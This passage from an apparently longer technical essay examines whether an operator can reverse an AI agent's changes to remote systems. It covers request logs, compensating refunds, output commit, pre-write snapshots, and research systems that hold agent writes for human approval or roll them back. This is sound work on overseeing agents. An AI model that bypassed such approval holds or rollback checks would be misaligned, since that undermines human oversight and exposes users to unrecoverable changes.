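If the first condition isn't met, the operator doesn't know what to restore. If the second isn't met, the operator knows what to restore but has no way to do it. If the third isn't met, restoring the old state erases someone's later work or leaves it referring to something that no longer exists. If the fourth isn't met, the remote system can be restored, but that doesn't undo what people did in reliance on the change.

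In *Can You Undo It?*, Waghmare and Sufi (2026) set nearly the same requirements for exactly restoring what an AI agent changed, but they treat later changes as a separate test. They point out that an audit log may meet the first requirement without meeting the others.

### What a request log lacks

An outbound request log often lacks even the old state, which is needed to undo a change. A PUT contains the new state, and a DELETE usually has no body. A POST that creates something is easier to undo, because the thing didn't exist before. A Git push is a partial exception, because it includes the old hash, which identifies the old state but doesn't contain it.

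A log that keeps response bodies may also happen to contain a before-image, because agents often read a record before changing it. For example, it may include the response to a GET of customer 88 from a minute earlier. That response is worth searching for, although someone else may have changed the plan between the agent's read and its write.

Undoing a change also requires permission, which the log doesn't provide. A token that can create charges can't necessarily delete them, and the operator may have removed the token from the log. Some actions, such as sending an email to someone outside the company, can't be undone at all.

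The last two conditions depend on other people, whose traffic doesn't pass through the agent's proxy. If a colleague edited customer 88 at 14:20, only the billing service has a record of it. If the customer read a notice about the new plan, there may be no record anywhere.

### Why a database can undo changes from its log

Databases routinely use a log to undo changes. They group operations into transactions, and the recovery log lets them return every item that a transaction updated to its value before the transaction, as Korth, Levy and Silberschatz explain in *A Formal Approach to Recovery by Compensating Transactions* (1990). If a second transaction has already read the new values, the database has to abort that one too, then any that read from the second, and so on. Most databases avoid these "cascading aborts" by hiding a transaction's changes from the others until it commits, meaning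 that it finishes and its changes become permanent.

| Condition | Database, before the commit | Request log on the agent's side |
|---|---|---|
| Before-image | In the recovery log | Usually missing |
| Permission and an operation | Built in | Depends on the service and the credential |
| No dependent changes | The database prevents or aborts them | Not shown |
| Nobody has seen it | The database hides the change | Not shown |

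A database can roll back a change because it controls the data, the log and all reads of the data, but it can do so only before the change is committed. Waghmare and Sufi tested a tool that lets agents update a small database. The tool committed each update before it returned a result, so by the time an agent could have noticed a mistake, the database's ROLLBACK command could no longer undo it.

An update could still be reversed if the old value had been saved first. The reverse command changed the row only if it still held the agent's value. It restored the row when nobody had edited it since, even if someone had edited a different row. When someone had edited the same row, the command left the newer value in place.

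Cruder methods of undoing changes lost people's work. In one test, an agent created a table and somebody else then added a row to it. Dropping the table returned the database to its original state but also deleted that row. Restoring a saved copy of a file erased a later edit every time, even when the edit was to a different paragraph from the one the agent had changed. The tests included only two or four versions of each case and no simultaneous edits, so real systems would be harder.

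### Output commit

Crash recovery raises the same problem. *A Survey of Rollback-Recovery Protocols in Message-Passing Systems* (Elnozahy, Alvisi and colleagues, 2002) describes programs on several machines that save checkpoints and restart from them after a failure. If one program goes back to a point before it sent a message, the receiver has to go back to a point before the message arrived. Otherwise the receiver's state includes a message that the sender's state shows as never sent.

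Some receivers of a system's output can't undo its effects. Elnozahy and colleagues give the examples of a printer, which can't unprint a character, and a cash machine, which can't recover money it has paid out. They call all such receivers the "outside world". Before the system sends them anything, it must make sure that no future failure will force it back to an earlier state. This is the output commit problem, and solving it delays the output.

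For a coding agent, the issue tracker, code host, package registry and billing service are all outside systems. If the operator restores the agent's session to 14:01, the agent loses its memory of the comment it posted at 14:02 and may well post it again. *ACRFence* (2026) surveyed 12 major agent frameworks and found that none ensures a tool call takes effect exactly once. One of the problems it lists for Google's framework is that rewinding the agent does not undo changes to outside systems.

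The older work is about crashes, but an operator is mostly worried about mistakes. To recover from a crash, it's enough to have saved the state that produced the output. Saving the agent's state doesn't show whether the comment was a good idea, so a person or program has to judge it before it is sent.

### What a refund leaves behind

After a command changes a remote system, the operator can often make a second change that offsets the first. *SAGAS* (Garcia-Molina and Salem, 1987) proposed this for long database transactions that delay shorter ones. A saga is a long transaction split into a sequence of smaller ones, between which other transactions can run. The database guarantees that it will either finish all the steps or run compensating transactions to amend the ones that finished.

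According to Korth and colleagues, compensating for a transaction guarantees a consistent state, but that state may differ from the one that would have existed without the transaction. Their example is a customer who returns a purchase. The sale may already have caused the shop to order more stock from its supplier and add the customer to a mailing list. Somebody has to use the shop's policy to decide whether to cancel the order, whether to keep the name on the list, and whether to refund the customer in cash or store credit, because the log doesn't contain those answers.

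Now suppose the billing script charged the wrong customer $60, the billing service collected the money from a card and emailed a receipt, and the operator refunded it the next day:

| | Before the charge | After the charge | After the refund |
|---|---|---|---|
| Net amount paid | $0 | $60 | $0 |
| Entries in the account's history | 0 | 1 | 2 |
| Emails to the customer | 0 | 1 | 2, if refunds also trigger one |
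| Time without the money | None | Still counting | About a day |

Only the first row returns to its old value. If the charge overdrew the customer's bank account, a $60 refund doesn't cover the bank's fee. A customer who saw the charge and cancelled the service may not come back.

The refund is also a remote effect, so its POST request can time out like the 37th charge, and a careless retry could refund the customer twice. Korth and colleagues require a compensating transaction to finish once it has started. A database can enforce this on its own transactions, but the operator can't make a billing company accept the refund.

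### The example session, sorted

Suppose the operator wants to take back everything from the example session:

| Change | Class | What the operator can do | Condition that fails |
|---|---|---|---|
| `main` points to the agent's commit | Restorable, for a while | Point it back | 1, if nobody still has the displaced commits; 3, once someone builds on the new version; 4, once someone fetches or deploys it |
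| 40 charges | Compensable | Refund them | 4: customers have paid and received notices |
| Version 2.3.1 | Permanent | Withdraw it if the registry's rules allow, or publish a correction | 4, once anyone downloads it; often 2 as well |
| The comment | Permanent | Delete it | 4, once anyone reads it or the notification email |

How much time the operator has to act matters more than the type of command. The operator might catch the force push before anyone fetches, but the tracker probably sends its notification emails within seconds.

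Classifications of this kind vary because people disagree about the fourth condition. *UndoBench* (2026), a set of recovery tests for agents, lists creating a Git release tag as reversible, a bank's dividend payment as compensatable and an urgent pager alert as irreversible. *L3M* (2026), which describes software for running agents, treats any `git push` as irreversible and instead limits which servers the agent may push to. Both are reasonable, since restoring a tag or branch reverses the change to the repository but doesn't make people forget code they have already seen.

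Waghmare and Sufi classified 536 tools that agents use through MCP servers. They judged that 203 of these change something, and labelled 115 of the 203 irreversible and only 31 restorable. Sufi then reviewed 150 of the tools, including all 31, and only two were rated restorable. An AI model proposed most of the review's ratings and Sufi approved them in batches, so the exact numbers deserve little weight. But the two sets of ratings differed partly over whether to count outsiders who might have seen the change, and if they are counted, very few actions are fully reversible.

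### Could the proxy read the old state first?

A terminating proxy can see a write coming, so it could fetch the before-image itself. For customer 88, it would work like this:

1. The proxy receives the PUT and pauses it.
2. It sends a GET to the same address and stores the reply, which shows that the customer is on the premium plan. It also stores the record's ETag.
3. It forwards the PUT with an `If-Match` header containing the ETag. If someone has changed the record since the GET, a server that supports this header refuses the write.
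4. To reverse the change later, the operator sends the stored state back, again on condition that the record still has the version the agent created.

This is an improvement, and it's probably worth doing for a simple record on a well-designed API. It meets the first condition, and step 4 protects later edits to the same record the same way Waghmare and Sufi's conditional update did.

Having the proxy save a copy of the record before each write fails in several ordinary cases. Without `If-Match`, someone can change the record between the GET and the PUT, making the stored copy out of date. The agent's credential may allow writing but not reading, so the proxy would need a second credential with wider access than the agent had. A GET may leave out fields that a PUT can set, such as a password. In the PocketOS incident, the before-image was a whole database, which no proxy would copy before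 forwarding a one-line request. If the server is still working on an earlier write that timed out, the proxy may read the record just before that write takes effect. *Fault-Tolerant Budget Conservation in Distributed Multi-Agent Delegation* (2026) cites a study of agents' tool calls which found that checking alone doesn't prevent such races.

The extra request also takes time. If each GET takes about 200 milliseconds, a script that makes 40 updates one after another will take eight seconds longer. The proxy's store of old records will also fill up with customers' data.

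Even a perfect copy doesn't meet the fourth condition, which limits how much it helps an operator. Waghmare and Sufi replayed 1,209 recorded runs in which nobody was attacking the agent, and found that a cautious policy would have made the agent stop for approval 1,904 times. When they let the agent proceed without approval if it could first save the old state of a private file, the total fell to 1,903. They allowed this only for additions to files, so a broader rule might reduce the total further, but not for changes that outsiders would see.

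### Agents with an undo function

Few agent systems have an undo function. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of long-running agents, found a rollback mechanism of any kind in 27 of 435 works.

In *GoEX*, an early attempt at this, Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) argued that people find it easier to judge an action's result than to judge the action in advance, so an agent should act first and let the user undo it. GoEX pairs each action with an undo action, which either a developer supplies or the language model writes. If the model's undo fails, GoEX records the failure for next time, so the model can be "wrong at most once". This doesn't help if the first failure leaves a customer's account deleted.

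GoEX can also save earlier versions of files in Git, and Patil and colleagues suggest, as a possible extension, copying an email before deleting it. For databases, GoEX can hold the transaction open until the user decides whether to keep the changes, but this makes other users wait. When an action can't be undone, GoEX limits the agent's permissions instead. One of its examples of an undo is deleting a sent Slack message, but people may already have read it.

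Later systems track how actions depend on each other. *SagaLLM* (2025) applies sagas to teams of agents and records the dependencies between operations, so that it can plan compensating actions when an operation fails. *SAFEFLOW* (2025) uses a similar dependency graph to roll back only the steps that a failure affects.

The best evidence that undo helps comes from STRATUS, a group of agents that repair faults in cloud services. Chen, Pan and colleagues (2025), in *STRATUS*, describe how it works:

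1. One agent at a time may make changes, and it records the state of the system before it starts.
2. It runs a repair of up to 20 commands. STRATUS rejects any command that has no undo, or replaces it with one that does, such as moving a file to a backup disk instead of deleting it.
3. It measures how bad the fault is now, from the number of alerts, broken service guarantees and unhealthy machines.
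4. If the score is worse than before, a separate agent undoes the commands in reverse order, and STRATUS can try another repair.

STRATUS running on GPT-4o solved nine of 13 repair problems in a simulated cloud. It solved three when it could retry but not undo, and two when it had only one attempt. The sample is small, but the gap is large, and it makes sense because a failed repair often left the system harder to fix.

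STRATUS can undo changes that a request log can't because its conditions resemble a database's. Cloud platforms such as Kubernetes store a description of how the system should look, which serves as the before-image, and the single-writer rule prevents other agents from making conflicting changes. The fourth condition hides a failed repair from other agents but not from customers. In one example, a bad repair raises the severity score from 15 to 30 before the undo brings it back to 15, and customers using the service in those minutes would see the worse state. Chen, Pan and colleagues acknowledge that perfect undo remains difficult when a change involves systems outside the cloud platform.

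### Could the proxy hold the write?

The proxy can hold a write until someone approves it, instead of trying to undo it afterward. This is a form of output commit in which a person decides whether to release the write. It is the only method here that addresses the fourth condition, because nobody can see a comment that hasn't been sent.

While a request is held for approval, the program that sent it waits for a reply. If approval takes ten minutes, curl or the billing script may give up first. The proxy could return a 202 to say it has queued the request, but a script that needs the new comment's ID can't continue without the real reply. The billing script probably waits for each reply before sending the next request, so without queueing, a reviewer would have to approve the charges one by one. Queueing lets the reviewer see all 40 together and much more easily spot a charge to the wrong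 customer.

A request can become wrong while it waits for review. An invoice that was right at 14:05 may be wrong at 15:00 because the customer has paid. The reviewer also has to recognise the mistake. Someone who saw only PocketOS's `volumeDelete` and an ID might have approved the deletion.

In *Atomix*, Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues (2026) present a system that delays only the actions it can't undo. In their example, an agent books a flight, a hotel and a car, then sends a confirmation email. Atomix lets the bookings go ahead, because it can cancel them (perhaps for a fee), but holds the email and tells the agent that it's queued. If the flight booking fails, Atomix cancels the other bookings and discards the email.

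They tested this with messages that should never have gone out, because an earlier step had failed or the plan had changed:

| Method | Invalid messages that got out, of 500 |
|---|---|
| No protection | 500 |
| Compensation, as in a saga | 400 |
| Restarting from a checkpoint | 200 |
| Atomix | 0 |
| Atomix, with the message wrongly labelled as reversible | 300 |

All the methods delivered the 500 valid messages. Two older methods of holding messages also released none of the invalid ones, but needed more code for each tool. The last row matters most to an operator because the protection depends on someone labelling each tool correctly.

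*Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) goes further and holds all effects until the end of the task. The agent works on a shadow copy of the files, while messages and other outside effects wait in an outbox. Cordon then checks the task as a whole, which can catch a problem that isn't visible in any single step, such as a secret that the agent read in a log file, summarised and then put in a message to colleagues. *Agentic Transaction* (2026) proposes a similar rule, in which effects spread only after validation.

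On 45 risky tasks, an agent without protection carried out the harmful action every time. Methods modelled on existing defences stopped it in time on 14 tasks, and Cordon stopped it on all 45. The researchers designed the tasks around the kinds of failure Cordon looks for, so this result shows that the design works, but not how often it would help in practice. With every action approved, the average task took 31.35 seconds instead of 25.55. The approvals followed a fixed policy, and a person reading each request would take longer.

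A script like `sync_billing.py` is hard for both systems to handle because they work at the level of the agent's tools, and the script makes 40 writes in a single tool call. Cordon blocks a shell command's network access by default. If the tool declares that it needs the network, Cordon sends its traffic through a proxy that records it and has a list of allowed hosts. The script's requests therefore seem to go out while it runs instead of waiting in the outbox. To hold them, an operator would need a terminating proxy that can pause individual requests.

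Holding writes doesn't make several of them succeed or fail together, either. If an approved task includes two emails, Atomix sends them one after the other, so if the second fails permanently, the first has already been sent. Mohammadi and colleagues write that software on the agent's side can't prevent this. The receiving services would have to support preparing both changes and then completing them together, which ordinary mail servers and web APIs can't do.
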